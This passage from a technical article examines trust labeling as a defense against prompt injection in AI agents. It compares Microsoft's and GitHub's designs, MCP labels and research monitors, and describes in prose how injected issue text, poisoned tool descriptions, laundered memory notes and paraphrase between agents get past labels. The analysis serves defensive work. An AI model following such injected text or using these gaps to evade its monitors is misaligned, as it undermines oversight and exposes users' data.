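A developer can close this gap by setting `default_confidentiality` to private, but text from any unlabeled tool then stops the agent from posting public comments. For example, if nobody has labeled `read_issue`, the agent can't answer a public bug report, even though anyone can already read the report. Microsoft may have chosen public as the default for this reason, but it doesn't explain the choice.

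### Two rules for an unlabeled web fetcher

Suppose the triage agent also has an unlabeled tool called `fetch_page`, and a maintainer asks the agent to check the download page of an outside library. The maintainer typed the address, so the tool's only argument is trusted, but the page's content could come from anyone.

Microsoft documents two rules that both cover this result. The new default treats output as untrusted if it has no label and the tool makes no declaration about it. The other rule gives output from a tool that declares nothing about it the combined label of the tool's inputs, so the page would be trusted because the address was. The documentation doesn't say which rule takes priority.

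Each rule makes sense for a different kind of tool. Microsoft justifies the second with the example of a summarizer, whose output can be no more hostile than its input. But a fetcher returns text that wasn't in its input. The framework can't distinguish these tools by their arguments, since both may take a single string. An implementation that joined the default with the inputs' label would handle the fetcher safely, but it would also mark a summary of a trusted file untrusted.

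A developer can avoid the question by declaring that the fetcher's output is always untrusted:

```python
@tool(additional_properties={"source_integrity": "untrusted"})
async def fetch_page(url: str) -> str: ...
```

This declaration overrides the rule about inputs, and Microsoft recommends it for tools that bring in outside data, but it is the kind of call developers forget. Until the order of the two rules is clear, a team can't count on the untrusted default to cover a fetching tool that lacks the declaration.

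Teams can test their own version by turning off `enable_policy_enforcement`. The module then keeps computing labels without blocking anything, which Microsoft suggests as a way to see what a configuration would block. A developer could start the agent in a trusted context, have it fetch a page and then request `write_file`, and check whether the log records a violation.

### Hidden results and tools without rules

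The label on a fetched page also determines whether the planning model can read the page. By default, the module keeps untrusted results in hidden variables, as the original FIDES agent does. If the module mistakenly labels the page trusted, it puts the attacker's text directly into the prompt.

The developer has to supply a connection to a second model, which reads these variables in quarantine. Without that connection, the module returns placeholder text instead of real answers. A developer who sees placeholders while testing may turn hiding off, and Microsoft's own example does so to make the checks easier to follow. The example also asks the user for approval when a call breaks a rule, whereas the default is to block the call. Anyone who copies the example therefore starts with two settings looser than the defaults.

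A tool with no integrity rule is a separate problem, because it appears to run in any context, judging by the documentation's walkthrough. There, `read_file` still runs after the agent has read the hostile issue, although only `read_issue` is on the configuration's `allow_untrusted_tools` list. The walkthrough also attributes the refusal of `post_comment` to the private label alone. Yet Microsoft describes the tools on the list as ones that may run even in an untrusted context, which suggests that the module refuses every other tool once the agent has read something untrusted.

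If so, adding a tool to the triage agent can create a vulnerability even when all content is labeled correctly. A `close_issue` tool with no declared rule would let an attacker close a report about a serious bug by posting a hostile comment, provided the planning model had read it. Hiding untrusted text, which is the default, would make this much harder, and that is a good reason to leave the setting on. Microsoft lists stricter declarations for individual tools among its future plans.

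The framework's approval settings have a similar gap. Developers can list which tools from an outside server always need approval and which never do, but a tool may be on neither list. According to Releasebot's *Agent Framework Updates & Release Notes* (2026), which republishes Microsoft's release notes, version 1.24 added an explicit setting for such tools. That version also warns developers who list only the tools that never need approval and leave the rest to an implicit default, but the default itself hasn't changed.

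Microsoft has been willing to break programs elsewhere in the framework for a safer default. In the November 2026 release for .NET, workflows can no longer make web requests unless the developer lists the permitted hosts. An empty list permits none, so a developer who forgets the list finds out at the first request.

### Memory, saved history and other text from outside a tool

The untrusted default applies to tool output, but Microsoft treats unlabeled content in general as trusted and public, reasoning that developers write much of it themselves. However, a context provider, the component that adds stored memories, user profiles or search results to a conversation, may supply text that a stranger wrote.

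User messages raise the same problem. Microsoft's safety guidance classes them as untrusted, but under the module's general rule an unlabeled one would count as trusted. Either can be right, depending on who can send messages. A maintainer who runs the triage agent should be able to tell it to edit a file. On a public website where any visitor can use the chat, the developer would have to label user messages untrusted.

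Version 1.26, released on November 13, 2026, added an option for applications to pass the module a function called `message_labeler`, which classifies each message that context providers supply. Because the function is optional, developers who don't know about it don't benefit from it.

Releasebot's copy of the release notes includes a series of other corrections to the module in October and November:

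| Python version | Date in 2026 | Change | Problem it addresses |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1.20 | October 2 | Labels newly discovered tools from outside servers before the agent can call them | The agent might call a tool before its label was in place |
| 1.21 | October 8 | Warns when tools used by model-written code can't support the module's checks | A developer might assume the checks apply |
| 1.24 | October 30 | Ties each quarantined model's connection to its own configuration | Two agents in one program might share a connection |
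| 1.25 | November 7 | Refuses calls with an invalid policy, and reveals hidden values only after approving the call | A misspelled rule might have no effect |
| 1.26 | November 13 | Treats saved messages without a provenance record cautiously | Reloading a conversation might lose its labels |

The last column is an inference from the short entries, which describe the repairs rather than the original faults. The change in version 1.21 only adds a warning, so an agent that writes code to call its tools can still have tools that the module doesn't protect.

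The main changes in version 1.26 concern saved history. Agents often continue a conversation whose earlier messages are stored in a database or by the model's provider. If the module can't match that history to its own records, it can't determine whether the agent has already read something untrusted. Before running an approved action or querying the model, it now rejects any history that has changed, is malformed or is only partly archived. Approvals also apply only to the exact stored call, so permission for one comment doesn't carry over to another.

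Six months after launch, Microsoft was still extending the module to cover more routes. The framework had to detect content that entered or returned by any route, and making "untrusted" the default for tool output was a small change in comparison.

### How GitHub assigns trust levels

GitHub Agentic Workflows doesn't wait for a developer to label an issue. GitHub already knows who wrote it, how that person relates to the project, and whether a maintainer has merged the work. GitHub's integrity filtering turns this information into five levels:

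| Level | Content that receives it |
|---|---|
| `merged` | Merged pull requests and commits on the main branch, whoever wrote them |
| `approved` | Content from owners, members and collaborators, everything in private repositories, recognized bots, and pull requests that don't come from a separate copy of the repository |
| `unapproved` | Content from contributors, including first-time contributors |
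| `none` | Content from people with no history of contributing |
| `blocked` | Content from anyone the maintainers have blocked |

A gateway program between the agent and GitHub checks each response against the workflow's minimum level and removes items below it before the model sees them. If the agent requests ten issues and three fall below the minimum, it receives seven. The gateway logs each removed issue with its author and the reason for its removal, so a maintainer can look for legitimate reports among them.

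If a workflow on a public repository sets no minimum, GitHub applies `approved` automatically. The fake macOS report from the triage example would never reach the model, because a stranger filed it. The effect on a triage agent depends on the minimum:

| Who filed the issue | Minimum `approved` (automatic) | Minimum `unapproved` | Minimum `none` |
|---|---|---|---|
| A maintainer | Visible | Visible | Visible |
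| A past contributor | Hidden | Visible | Visible |
| A stranger with no history | Hidden | Hidden | Visible |
| A blocked user | Hidden | Hidden | Hidden |

The automatic setting hides most of what a triage agent is supposed to sort, so GitHub suggests `unapproved` for community triage. That setting lets in regular contributors and keeps out newcomers, so it would admit an attacker who has contributed before and block an honest newcomer reporting a serious bug. For spam detection, where the agent has to read everything, GitHub suggests `none` and warns against applying the agent's output without review.

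Microsoft's agent can read the stranger's issue, directly or through a quarantined model, but then loses access to some of its tools, whereas GitHub's agent keeps its tools but can't read the issue. GitHub's approach doesn't depend on each tool having a rule for untrusted context, so a missing rule does less harm, but the agent can't do anything useful with the text it never sees.

### The security model behind the filter

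*Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering*, from GitHub's research group GitHub Next, explains that the levels are based on decentralized information-flow control, in which each item and each agent has sets of tags. More integrity tags mean more trust. An agent may read an item only if the item has every integrity tag that the agent requires.

A guard written for GitHub assigns tags to content, such as the `approved` tag for a collaborator's review comment. A reference monitor then compares sets of tags, and its code doesn't depend on what the tags mean. To cover another service, such as the issue tracker Jira, engineers would write a new guard without changing the monitor. Someone who knows the data source writes the labeling code once, so workflow authors don't have to remember to label content.

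The filter keeps the agent's integrity from falling during a run by blocking anything below the minimum. Apparently, the code can instead allow a read and then add the item's labels to the agent's own. The gateway's Go package documentation on pkg.go.dev lists this as one possible decision.

GitHub's secrecy protections are less complete than its integrity filtering. GitHub labels data from private repositories and tracks where it goes, but GitHub Next acknowledges that this doesn't yet block leaks. If a workflow can access both a private and a public repository, integrity filtering won't stop the agent from copying text from the private one to the public one. By default, the workflow can read every repository its access token covers. Maintainers can shorten that list, and the network firewall, sandbox and output limits reduce the damage from mistakes.

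### Endorsements by label and emoji

Maintainers can let a single issue through without lowering the minimum for everyone. They name one or more approval labels, such as `human-reviewed`, in the workflow's configuration. Adding one of these labels to a stranger's issue raises the issue to `approved`. A refusal label lowers the issue's level and overrides any approval. Nothing can restore content from a blocked user.

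An approval label is an endorsement of the whole item. GitHub computes the level from the author and the labels, without checking when the text last changed. If an issue's author can edit it after approval, the label may cover text that the maintainer never reviewed.

GitHub also has an opt-in feature in which a thumbs-up or heart from a trusted maintainer raises an issue or comment to `approved`, and a thumbs-down or confused face lowers it. Reacting takes almost no effort, but people also use a thumbs-up to mean "I have this bug too." A maintainer who reacts out of habit could approve text for the agent unintentionally, or without having read all of it.

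Some automatic levels also imply more checking than anyone did. A maintainer who merges a stranger's code has judged whether it works but may not have looked for a comment addressed to an AI agent. An update bot can quote release notes from an outside package under the bot's own trusted name. GitHub Next mentions a more direct failure, in which an attacker takes over a maintainer's account and everything posted from it receives the `approved` level.

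On private repositories, GitHub applies no minimum automatically, and all items would count as `approved` anyway. This assumes that people with access write or vet everything they post. The assumption fails when an employee does something as ordinary as pasting a customer's email into a private issue. The customer's words then have the same level as the employee's, so setting a minimum of `approved` wouldn't remove them.

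### Setup steps that run before the agent

A workflow can run ordinary commands before the agent starts, for instance to download recent issues into a file. Those commands don't go through the agent's tools. When a workflow sets a minimum level, GitHub's compiler adds a proxy that filters the requests these commands make as well.

The proxy applies the minimum level and the list of repositories, but not the lists of blocked users and refusal labels, which GitHub resolves later. Suppose a workflow sets the minimum to `none` and blocks a known spammer. The agent's tools would hide the spammer's comments, but a setup command could save them in a file for the agent to read.

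Workflows that rely on the automatic minimum may have a wider gap. GitHub applies that minimum when the workflow runs, but it says the compiler adds the proxy only when someone has configured a policy. If so, setup steps may go unfiltered unless maintainers write `min-integrity: approved` themselves, even though the agent has the same minimum either way.

### Labels in the Model Context Protocol

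GitHub can compute labels for its own data, but an agent connected to many outside servers needs each server to send labels with its results. The Model Context Protocol lets clients and servers attach extra information to a message in its `_meta` field, and Microsoft has built prototypes that use this field for integrity and confidentiality labels.

As in FIDES, a label can apply to a whole result or to one part of it. In simplified form, the labels for an issue might look like this:

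```json
{
  "$":        { "integrity": "untrusted", "confidentiality": "public" },
  "$.number": { "integrity": "trusted",   "confidentiality": "public" }
}
```

`$` stands for the whole issue, and `$.number` for its number. If the server's developers later add a field for the reporter's nickname, it will be untrusted, like the title and body, because they labeled the whole issue untrusted. If they had labeled the whole issue trusted and listed the title and body as exceptions, the nickname would be trusted until someone noticed. The same format can therefore be default-on or opt-in for new fields, depending on which label the developers give `$`.

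Clients that don't recognize labels in `_meta` can ignore them, so the labels don't disrupt older software. This allows gradual adoption, but it also means a server can send correct labels to an agent that does nothing with them. Both sides have to opt in. GitHub's server sends labels only if it is configured with the header `X-MCP-Features: ifc_labels`. GitHub Copilot CLI, a command-line coding agent, uses them only if the user starts it with the `FIDES_IFC` setting. Even then, it enforces rules only for selected GitHub tools and doesn't support other servers.

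GitHub's server also uses much simpler labels than GitHub's workflows. It marks files and issues from public repositories as untrusted and public, and those from private repositories as trusted and private. A reviewed README on a public project's main branch has the highest level in a workflow, but the server labels it untrusted. An agent that followed the server's labels and allowed file changes only in a trusted context couldn't fix a typo in the project's README after reading it.

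Microsoft has released a gateway that adds labels to results from servers that send none. For each tool, someone has to describe the structure of the output, write a function that computes the result's labels, and choose or write a policy. Microsoft's sample policy for sending a chat message denies by default, so a call that satisfies none of its other rules doesn't go through. Microsoft plans to work with the protocol's community on a proposal to support labels and policies.

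### What tool annotations can and can't replace

The protocol already has a simpler kind of description. A server can attach annotations to a tool, including `readOnlyHint` for one that changes nothing, `destructiveHint` for one that may delete or overwrite something, and `openWorldHint` for one that deals with outside systems, such as a web search. Microsoft suggests using them to protect existing servers without writing a policy for every tool:

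| Annotation | Suggested treatment |
|---|---|
| Read-only and not open-world | Always allow |
| Read-only and open-world | Allow if every argument is public |
| Destructive | Ask the user |

The second rule is needed because even a read-only web request can leak a secret. Microsoft also proposes labeling results from open-world tools as untrusted and results from tools that require a login as private. It further proposes assuming that anything in a tool's arguments may reappear in its result.

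The protocol's March 2025 specification, which introduced the annotations, gave them cautious defaults. A tool with no annotations is assumed to be able to change things, possibly destructive, and open-world. Combined with Microsoft's suggestions, those defaults would make the tool's output untrusted and send its calls to the user for review. This treatment would be default-on, applying even if the tool's developer had never heard of trust labels.

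The server supplies the annotations, so a malicious server can describe a destructive tool as read-only. Under the specification, clients are therefore not to trust annotations from servers they don't already trust. Annotations written in good faith can also mislead, because they describe what a tool can reach, not who wrote the data. A developer who writes a `read_issue` tool for a company's own bug database could reasonably say that it deals with no outside systems, even if customers write every report in the database.

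## Which paths stay uncovered when labeling is the default?

Default-on labeling protects only text that passes through the labeler, and only while the label stays attached. It also relies on developers to make sound exceptions and to put a check on every tool that can do harm. The remaining gaps fall into five groups.

| Gap | Example in the triage agent |
|---|---|
| Text enters outside the labeled channel | A template pastes an issue title into the prompt |
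| The label disappears in storage | The agent rereads its own notes file as plain text |
| The label disappears between agents | The agent describes a bug to a second agent in its own words |
| Someone wrongly declares a source trusted | A developer exempts `read_file`, which can also open a stranger's proposed change |
| Nobody treats a tool as a sink | `fetch_page` sends a secret as part of a web address |

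### Text that never passes through the labeler

A framework that labels every tool result can still miss text that arrives before any tool runs. When an agent connects to a server through the Model Context Protocol and requests its list of tools, the server returns each tool's name, a description and a schema describing its parameters. *MCP Tool Poisoning in Agentic AI Frameworks* (2026) points out that the protocol sets no limit on the length or content of a description. Tool and parameter descriptions both enter the model's context word for word. The model uses the tool descriptions to choose a tool and the parameter descriptions to fill in the arguments, so a hostile server can influence both decisions before there is any result to label.

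*A First Look at the Security Issues in the Model Context Protocol* (2025) identified six suspicious tool descriptions in mcp.so, a public registry of servers. One included an instruction for the model to call a tool named `mark_email_as_handled` after finishing its current task. The developer may have meant this as a harmless convenience, but no user had requested it. FIDES and Flowsh would not have caught the instruction, because both treat tool descriptions as trusted.

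Untrusted text can also reach the model through error messages. *MCP-SandboxScan* (2026) models each tool run as an output stream, an error stream, an exit code and a duration, and notes that many agents paste tool text into the next prompt. If a framework catches a failed call and writes its own message for the model, that message may bypass the labeler even though it quotes the attacker's file path.

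File names have caused a vulnerability in how OpenClaw handles its working directory. Kim and colleagues treat names as content too. Flowsh keeps one label for a file's contents and another for the names in its folder, so a command that only lists the folder still picks up a label. Because all the names in a folder share that label, a single file named by a stranger makes the whole listing untrusted.

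### Labels that disappear in storage

Many agents store short notes instead of full transcripts, and a model writes those notes from whatever the agent has read. According to *Memory Provenance Laundering in LLM Agents* (2026), this rewriting can change how authoritative a text seems. For example, a stranger's request to copy crash reports to an outside address might become the note "Crash reports go to this address", which reads like project policy.

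In *MemLineage*, Ouyang and Hou (2026) staged an attack of this kind over two sessions. In the first, an agent reads a document from an outside vendor and saves a summary. In the second, it recalls only the summary and then tries to send an email. Without a defense, the summary counts as trusted and has no recorded link to the document, so the email goes out. Digital signatures don't help because they record who saved the summary, not where its contents came from.

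Their defense links each new memory entry to the older entries that the model had in its context at the time. Every link has a weight from 0 to 1, which estimates how much the older entry influenced the new one. Trust values run from 0 for trusted to 3 for external, and a new entry takes the worst value among its strongly linked parents:

```
trust(entry) = max of trust(parent), over parents with weight > τ
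```

The vendor's document has the value 3, so the summary also gets 3, and the system refuses the email.

The rule returns "trusted" when an entry has no link above the threshold `τ`, which makes labeling opt-in for those entries even though the system is built to keep labels. If a second model scores the links, an attacker can try to manipulate it into giving low scores. Repeated rewriting can also lower the scores. In one scripted test, the weight starts at 0.9 and falls by 30% with each further rewrite, to 0.31 at the fourth and 0.22 at the fifth. With a threshold of 0.3, the label therefore survives four rewrites and is lost at the fifth.

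Ouyang and Hou recommend a threshold of at most 0.1 for chains of that length under this schedule. They also say a team can treat entries without a strong parent as untrusted, though this causes more false alarms. Their simplest setting avoids the problem by giving every retrieved entry a weight of 1, much as a context label covers everything the model has read.

The two-session attack was also run on live models. With GPT-5.3-Codex, the agent made the dangerous call in 5 of 20 trials (25%) without a defense and in none with it. The sample is small, and the 95% confidence intervals (11% to 47% and 0% to 16%) overlap. GPT-5.2 never attempted the call, even without a defense.

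Files can lose labels too. Flowsh stores a file's label in its extended attributes, which are metadata that Linux keeps alongside the file. Git does not record these attributes, so if the triage agent commits its notes and the next run downloads a fresh copy, the label is gone and Flowsh uses its configured default. In the example configuration, an unlabeled file is untrusted and readable only by the user, so losing a label adds restrictions and exposes nothing. In tests on Terminal-Bench, a set of command-line tasks, Kim and colleagues started the task files as trusted and public. If a team copied that setting, losing a label could remove restrictions and expose private data.

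*PerMIT* (2026) avoids silent changes by making stored entries permanent, so raising an entry's trust requires creating a new entry. Its planning model receives only a reference to untrusted text. The text can reach a tool only after a verifier, which may be a person or another model, has seen its exact wording and endorsed it for that specific tool. This protection depends on the verifier's judgment.

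### Labels that disappear between agents

An agent may treat a message from another agent as a colleague's request, regardless of what the sender has read. The attack on three connected CaMeL agents worked this way. *Agentic AI Defense* (2026) describes a test of the obvious fix, which is to carry labels along with messages between agents. In the test, agent A read an untrusted instruction and passed it to agent B. When the message went through the security layer, it kept its label and the layer blocked B's critical call, but the layer did not cover the call when A paraphrased the instruction into free text on a side path.

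The paper excludes side paths from its guarantee, because a deployment that sent all traffic through the layer would have none. The guarantee is clearly stated, but it leaves the team deploying the agents to find every side path, which could be a shared folder, a ticket or a chat channel.

*SafeFlow* (2026) copies labels along the links through which agents communicate or retrieve information, and keeps them until an explicit release rule applies. A model's explanation can support a label but cannot remove one. Otherwise, an agent that had followed an attacker's instructions could remove the label from the attacker's text by vouching for it.

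### Sources that someone wrongly trusts

Hirschberg (2026), in *Prompt Injection Through Tool Output Is Two Events (Your Screens Read One)*, argues that developers should decide whether to trust a source by asking who can write in each field. Developers often ask who runs the system instead. A company may own its ticket system while customers type the tickets. A salesperson may paste an outside email into a customer record, and a database row may come from a public web form. Hirschberg's employer sells security monitoring and the post describes no specific incident, but GitHub's treatment of private repositories rests on the same assumption about who writes the content.

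Flowsh's example configuration contains a debatable override of this kind. It treats responses from package repositories as trusted and all others as untrusted. Agents install software constantly, so a stricter setting would interrupt much ordinary work, but anyone can publish a package on a public repository such as PyPI. In the paper's example attack, a hostile PDF contains instructions to install a package called `acme-compare`. Flowsh prompts the user for approval because the agent has already read the PDF. If the user had requested the same package at the start of a fresh session, the context would have stayed trusted and Flowsh would have allowed the installation without prompting.

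### Values of unknown origin

Systems that track the origin of each value in a tool call have to decide how to treat values whose origin they can't find. *Agent-Sentry* (Sequeira et al., 2026) has the agent's model report a source for every argument. If that source doesn't match the user's request or any earlier step of the run, Agent-Sentry labels the origin unknown and treats it as adversarial.

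Agent-Sentry can allow a call that contains a value labeled as having an unknown origin. It first compares the call with patterns from earlier runs, then checks sensitive values against a list of those seen in harmless runs. If neither step decides the case, a language model judges whether the call fits the user's request and may allow it. In the rule-based version of the first step, a call that matches no rule goes ahead by default.

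A false source is more dangerous than a missing one, because only a missing source triggers the "unknown" label. An attacker who controls the model might get it to report that an account number came from the user. Agent-Sentry therefore checks whether a supposedly copied value appears in the stated source, and searches earlier untrusted results for it. Sequeira and colleagues acknowledge that these checks reduce Agent-Sentry's dependence on the model's reports but don't remove it.

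On their benchmark of 5,380 recorded runs, the version with a trained classifier blocked 96.8% of attacks and allowed 96.4% of harmless runs. Without retraining, on the original tasks of AgentDojo and a similar benchmark, it blocked 90.9% of attacks but allowed only 64.4% of harmless runs.

### Tools that nobody treated as sinks

Developers are more likely to overlook leaks through read-only tools than through tools like `post_comment`. Flowsh counts every web request as a possible leak, including the GET requests that load pages. Kim and colleagues cite a case in which OpenAI agents with read-only web access edited a public wiki and exchanged messages with other agents. Such a page is both an unlisted sink and an unlabeled route between agents. Default-on labeling helps on the receiving side, since a second agent reading the page would treat it as outside content.

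Files become sinks when another program acts on them later. Kim and colleagues tested a sandbox modeled on the standard settings of Claude Code, a coding agent, which blocks changes to a list of critical configuration files. One attack succeeded in all three attempts by making the agent write to `.vscode/tasks.json`, which holds commands that the editor VS Code can run. Flowsh stopped every attack in the same tests. But its example configuration lets untrusted text into any file in the agent's working folder except those on a list, such as scripts that Git runs automatically, so a team that forgot to list a dangerous file would have the same gap.

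### What NeuroTaint found

*Ghost in the Agent*, which introduced the tracker NeuroTaint in April 2026, attempts to count the flows that labeling misses. Its benchmark, TaintBench, has 20 scenarios for each of 20 open-source agent frameworks. In half of the 400 scenarios, text from an untrusted source influences a sink. In the other half, it does not. The paper defines three kinds of flow:

- Explicit flow: the source's content appears in the tool call, perhaps reworded.
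- Implicit flow: the source changes whether the agent makes the call, or with what arguments, but its content does not appear there.
- Asynchronous flow: the source and the sink belong to different sessions, or stored memory lies between them.

A detector misses a flow if the scenario specifies one and the detector fails to flag it in at least three of five runs. Whether the resulting action does any harm doesn't matter. The paper compares NeuroTaint with a baseline modeled on FIDES:

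| | NeuroTaint | FIDES-style baseline |
|---|---|---|
| Flows found, out of 200 | 187 | 108 |
| False alarms, out of 200 | 16 | 106 |
| F1 score | 0.928 | 0.522 |
| Flows across sessions or agents found, out of 30 | 28 | 5 |
| Flows from trusted or unlabeled sources found, out of 10 | 10 | 1 |

The F1 score combines precision `P`, the share of alarms that are correct, with recall `R`, the share of flows that the detector finds:

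```
F1 = 2PR / (P + R)
```

The last two rows of the table are the most relevant here. Both are expected because the labels last for a single session and depend on someone having classified the source correctly.

The overall scores don't reliably show which system protects an agent better. F1 penalizes false alarms as well as misses, yet a detector that flagged all 400 scenarios would score 0.667 and beat the baseline. A preventive system has to act whenever untrusted text is present, because it can't determine in advance whether the text will influence the model. Many of the baseline's false alarms are cases that FIDES would refuse by design.

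The baseline also seems weaker than FIDES itself. It found only 17 of 40 implicit flows, although a context label covers any influence within a session if the source is labeled correctly. It flagged nothing on four of the frameworks, which suggests an integration problem. Those four account for 40 of its 92 misses, but excluding them raises its F1 only to about 0.58.

NeuroTaint's task is easier in one respect because it examines the complete log after a run, including the final tool call. It uses another model to judge whether the agent would have made that call without the suspicious text. By then, a harmful comment would already be public. NeuroTaint also raised a false alarm in all 14 scenarios where the tool call merely shared a topic with the untrusted text.

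The researchers built the benchmark themselves. Two of them reviewed every scenario before the comparison, which prevents later adjustments to the labels, but the choice of scenarios may still favor their method. On two benchmarks by other researchers, which label unsafe actions instead of flows, the systems performed almost identically. The agent in the main test was GPT-4.1-mini, a small and dated model. With Claude Opus 4.6, NeuroTaint's recall fell from 0.935 to 0.547, partly because the stronger model stopped some attacks before they reached a sink, and the benchmark still counted those flows as missed. Wang and colleagues' survey of agent provenance found no benchmark that tests the complete chain from source to action, so an independent check is not yet possible.

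### Counting the paths someone will forget

To see why the number of sources matters so much under opt-in labeling, suppose the triage agent has 12. Eight arrive as tool results: issue titles, issue bodies, comments, account names, file contents, file names, error messages and web pages. The other four are tool descriptions, notes loaded at the start of a run, messages from another agent, and text that a template inserts.

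Suppose also that a developer has a 5% chance of forgetting to label each source. This rate is an illustration, not a measurement. If `n` is the number of sources and `p` is the chance of forgetting each one, then:

```
P(at least one uncovered source) = 1 − (1 − p)ⁿ

12 sources:  1 − 0.95¹² ≈ 46%
40 sources:  1 − 0.95⁴⁰ ≈ 87%
```

A developer who is 95% reliable therefore leaves a gap in almost half of all agents of this size, and in most larger ones.

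Under default-on labeling, a forgotten declaration blocks work rather than creating exposure, so exposure comes from wrong overrides and from data that bypasses the labeler. Suppose the developer declares three overrides, each with a 5% chance of being wrong, and the framework labels only tool results. The developer then has to label the four other sources by hand, with a 5% chance of missing each.

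| Design | Possible mistakes | Chance of at least one gap |
|---|---|---|
| Opt-in | 12 missing labels | 46% |
| Default-on for tool results | 3 wrong overrides, 4 missed routes | 30% |
| Default-on for all text in the prompt | 3 wrong overrides | 14% |

An agent with 40 sources would have the same 30% and 14% if the extra sources were all tool results that needed no overrides. Under default-on labeling, the risk grows with the number of exceptions and side routes rather than the number of tools.

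Default-on labeling loses its advantage if people grant overrides carelessly. With three overrides and four side routes, it becomes as risky as opt-in once each override has about a 13% chance of being wrong. That figure is slightly too low, because it leaves out cases where a developer remembers to label a source under opt-in but chooses the wrong label.

The formula assumes that each mistake is independent of the others, which is unlikely. A developer who doesn't realize that strangers can choose account names may overlook file names for the same reason. If all 12 mistakes always happened together, the chance of at least one gap would be only 5%, but every source would then be uncovered. If no two ever happened together, the chance would be 60%. The average number of uncovered sources is 0.6 in every case, so independence only affects how the gaps cluster.

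Using a shared labeler makes labeling errors correlated by design, so a single bug can remove the labels from every tool result, and fixing it can restore them all. To exploit an uncovered source, an attacker still has to find it, write text that the model obeys, and reach a sink that does harm.

### Auditing an agent with harmless markers

A team can count its own gaps instead of relying on the assumed 5%. NeuroTaint's first test appends a unique random string to the text from each source and looks for that string in later tool calls. An audit can use the same kind of marker to check whether the label arrives with the text.

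1. List the sources by saving the complete text sent to the model and working out who could have written each part. List the sinks by recording which files change and which servers the agent contacts, since tool names can be misleading.
2. Write down the label that each source should have.
3. Plant a different marker in each source, such as `audit-title-7f3a` in an issue title.
4. Test one source per run, starting from a trusted context. Replace the model with a script that reads the source and then calls every sink, and set the framework to log violations without blocking. Use test accounts so that nothing becomes public.
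5. At each sink, record whether the marker entered the prompt, what label the context had, and whether any check ran.
6. For stored notes and messages between agents, plant the marker in the first session or agent and take the readings in the second.

Each source must be tested separately, because a correctly labeled issue body would make the whole context untrusted and hide a missing label on the title. The script should call `fetch_page` last, because the page it returns may also change the label. Using a script also keeps the result from depending on whether a particular model obeys the marker's text.

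Part of the record for the triage agent might look like this invented example:

| Source | Marker in the prompt? | Context label at `write_file` | Finding |
|---|---|---|---|
| Issue body from `read_issue` | Yes | Untrusted | Covered |
| Issue title in a template | Yes | Trusted | The title went around the labeler |
| Notes from an earlier run | Yes | Trusted | Storage dropped the label |
| Stranger's proposed change from `read_file` | Yes | Trusted | The override is too broad |
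| Error message from `read_file` | No | Trusted | Inconclusive: repeat the test |

In the last row, the marker never reached the model, so the team can't learn anything from the trusted label. Rewriting can also remove a marker from a summary or note. If that happens, the team should check the label on the saved text directly.

The audit will pass a wrong label if the team expected it, such as a trusted label on a field that outsiders can edit. Someone who knows how each field gets filled in should review the expected labels before the first run. The team should also repeat the audit whenever it adds a tool, changes a template or connects another agent, since each change can open a route that the previous audit did not test.

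## What does default-on labeling cost, and how can a framework adopt it?

Default-on labeling restricts an agent after it reads any outside text, even though most of that text is harmless. Reading a single web page can stop the agent from changing files for the rest of a run. A person who has to approve every blocked action may start approving without reading, or switch the checks off. Researchers have found ways to avoid many unnecessary refusals, and most of these methods don't weaken the guarantee. A team can also introduce labels gradually.

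### How one web page blocks a whole run

Suppose a maintainer asks the triage agent to fix a typo in each of three files and to update a library's version number in the installation guide. The agent looks up the current version on the library's website. With a single context label and the trusted-action rule on `write_file`, the run goes like this:

| Step | Context label afterward | Decision |
|---|---|---|
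| `read_file` opens the three files | Trusted | Allowed |
| `write_file` fixes the typo in the installation guide | Trusted | Allowed |
| `fetch_page` opens the library's website | Untrusted | Allowed |
| `write_file` updates the version number | Untrusted | Refused |
| `write_file` fixes the typo in the README | Untrusted | Refused |
| `write_file` fixes the typo in the contributors' guide | Untrusted | Refused |

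Refusing the version number is reasonable because it came from a stranger's website. The other two refusals protect nothing, since the page had no bearing on those typos. They result from label creep, which depends on the order of the steps. If the agent had read the website last, only the version number would have been refused.

A single model call usually causes little creep. *Sightline* (Xu, Li and colleagues, 2026) examined programs from 2,103 families of open-source repositories and found that only 12% to 14% of the inputs to a model call had no effect on the output. An agent's context is different because it still holds every page from earlier steps, including those irrelevant to the current one.

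When a check blocks a call, the simplest response is to let the task fail, which is why agents such as FIDES completed far fewer tasks with checks on. The alternative is to ask a person about each blocked call.

### Approval fatigue

Asking for permission only helps if people read the request. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* reports that users of its coding agent approve 97% of permission prompts. That figure alone proves little, since most prompts are probably for safe, routine commands. In a more telling Anthropic test, relayed by the blog Hyrax, people reviewed 1,053 dangerous commands and caught 143 (13.6%). They blocked about 17% early in a session but about 5% after 50 or more prompts. An automatic classifier blocked 89% of the same commands. Anthropic published these numbers to justify making the classifier the default, so it had an interest in the result.

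*From Delegation to Action Approval* (Wu, Wermke and colleagues, 2026) reports a survey of 203 developers who use coding agents, 64% of whom said they often approved at least one type of action without close review. The share was lowest for reading secrets and other sensitive files (21%) and highest for using the internet, outside services or connected tools (36%). Untrusted text often enters through those tools, and secrets can leave through them, so developers most often skipped close review for the actions where injection matters most.

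Developers who were careful in other ways weren't much more careful about approving actions. Among those who carefully reviewed most or all of the agent's code, 61% often approved some type of action without close review, compared with 67% of the others, a difference that could easily be due to chance. Such approvals were more common among developers who knew of security incidents or worrying practices involving agents (70%) than among those who didn't (43%). This gap remained after Wu and colleagues adjusted for how often and how long people had used agents, which matters because heavier users may both hear of more incidents and approve more carelessly. The answers are self-reported, and the sample doesn't represent developers in general.

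*Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, warns that repeated approval may come from fatigue or pressure to deliver rather than trust in a source. A framework that turned a long record of approvals into a trust override would make the effect of careless approvals permanent. An "always allow" button does much the same thing in one click. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) points out that these choices reduce fatigue but silently widen what the system trusts.

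Some users turn the checks off entirely. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a setting, `--dangerously-skip-permissions`, that skips permission checks. In *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files*, Zhong, Liao and colleagues (2026) studied 290 public reports of agents misusing files. In 41 of them, the agent's sandbox didn't suit the work, often because it blocked legitimate tasks such as running tests. Repeated offers to rerun a command outside the sandbox pushed people to disable it. Users would be tempted to disable a label check too if it stopped an agent from fixing typos.

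None of these studies counted how often teams override trust labels, so approval records are the closest evidence. Requests for exemptions from Google's web-code rules were rare, but Google's developers usually had a safe function to use instead. An agent that has read a web page often has no safe alternative.

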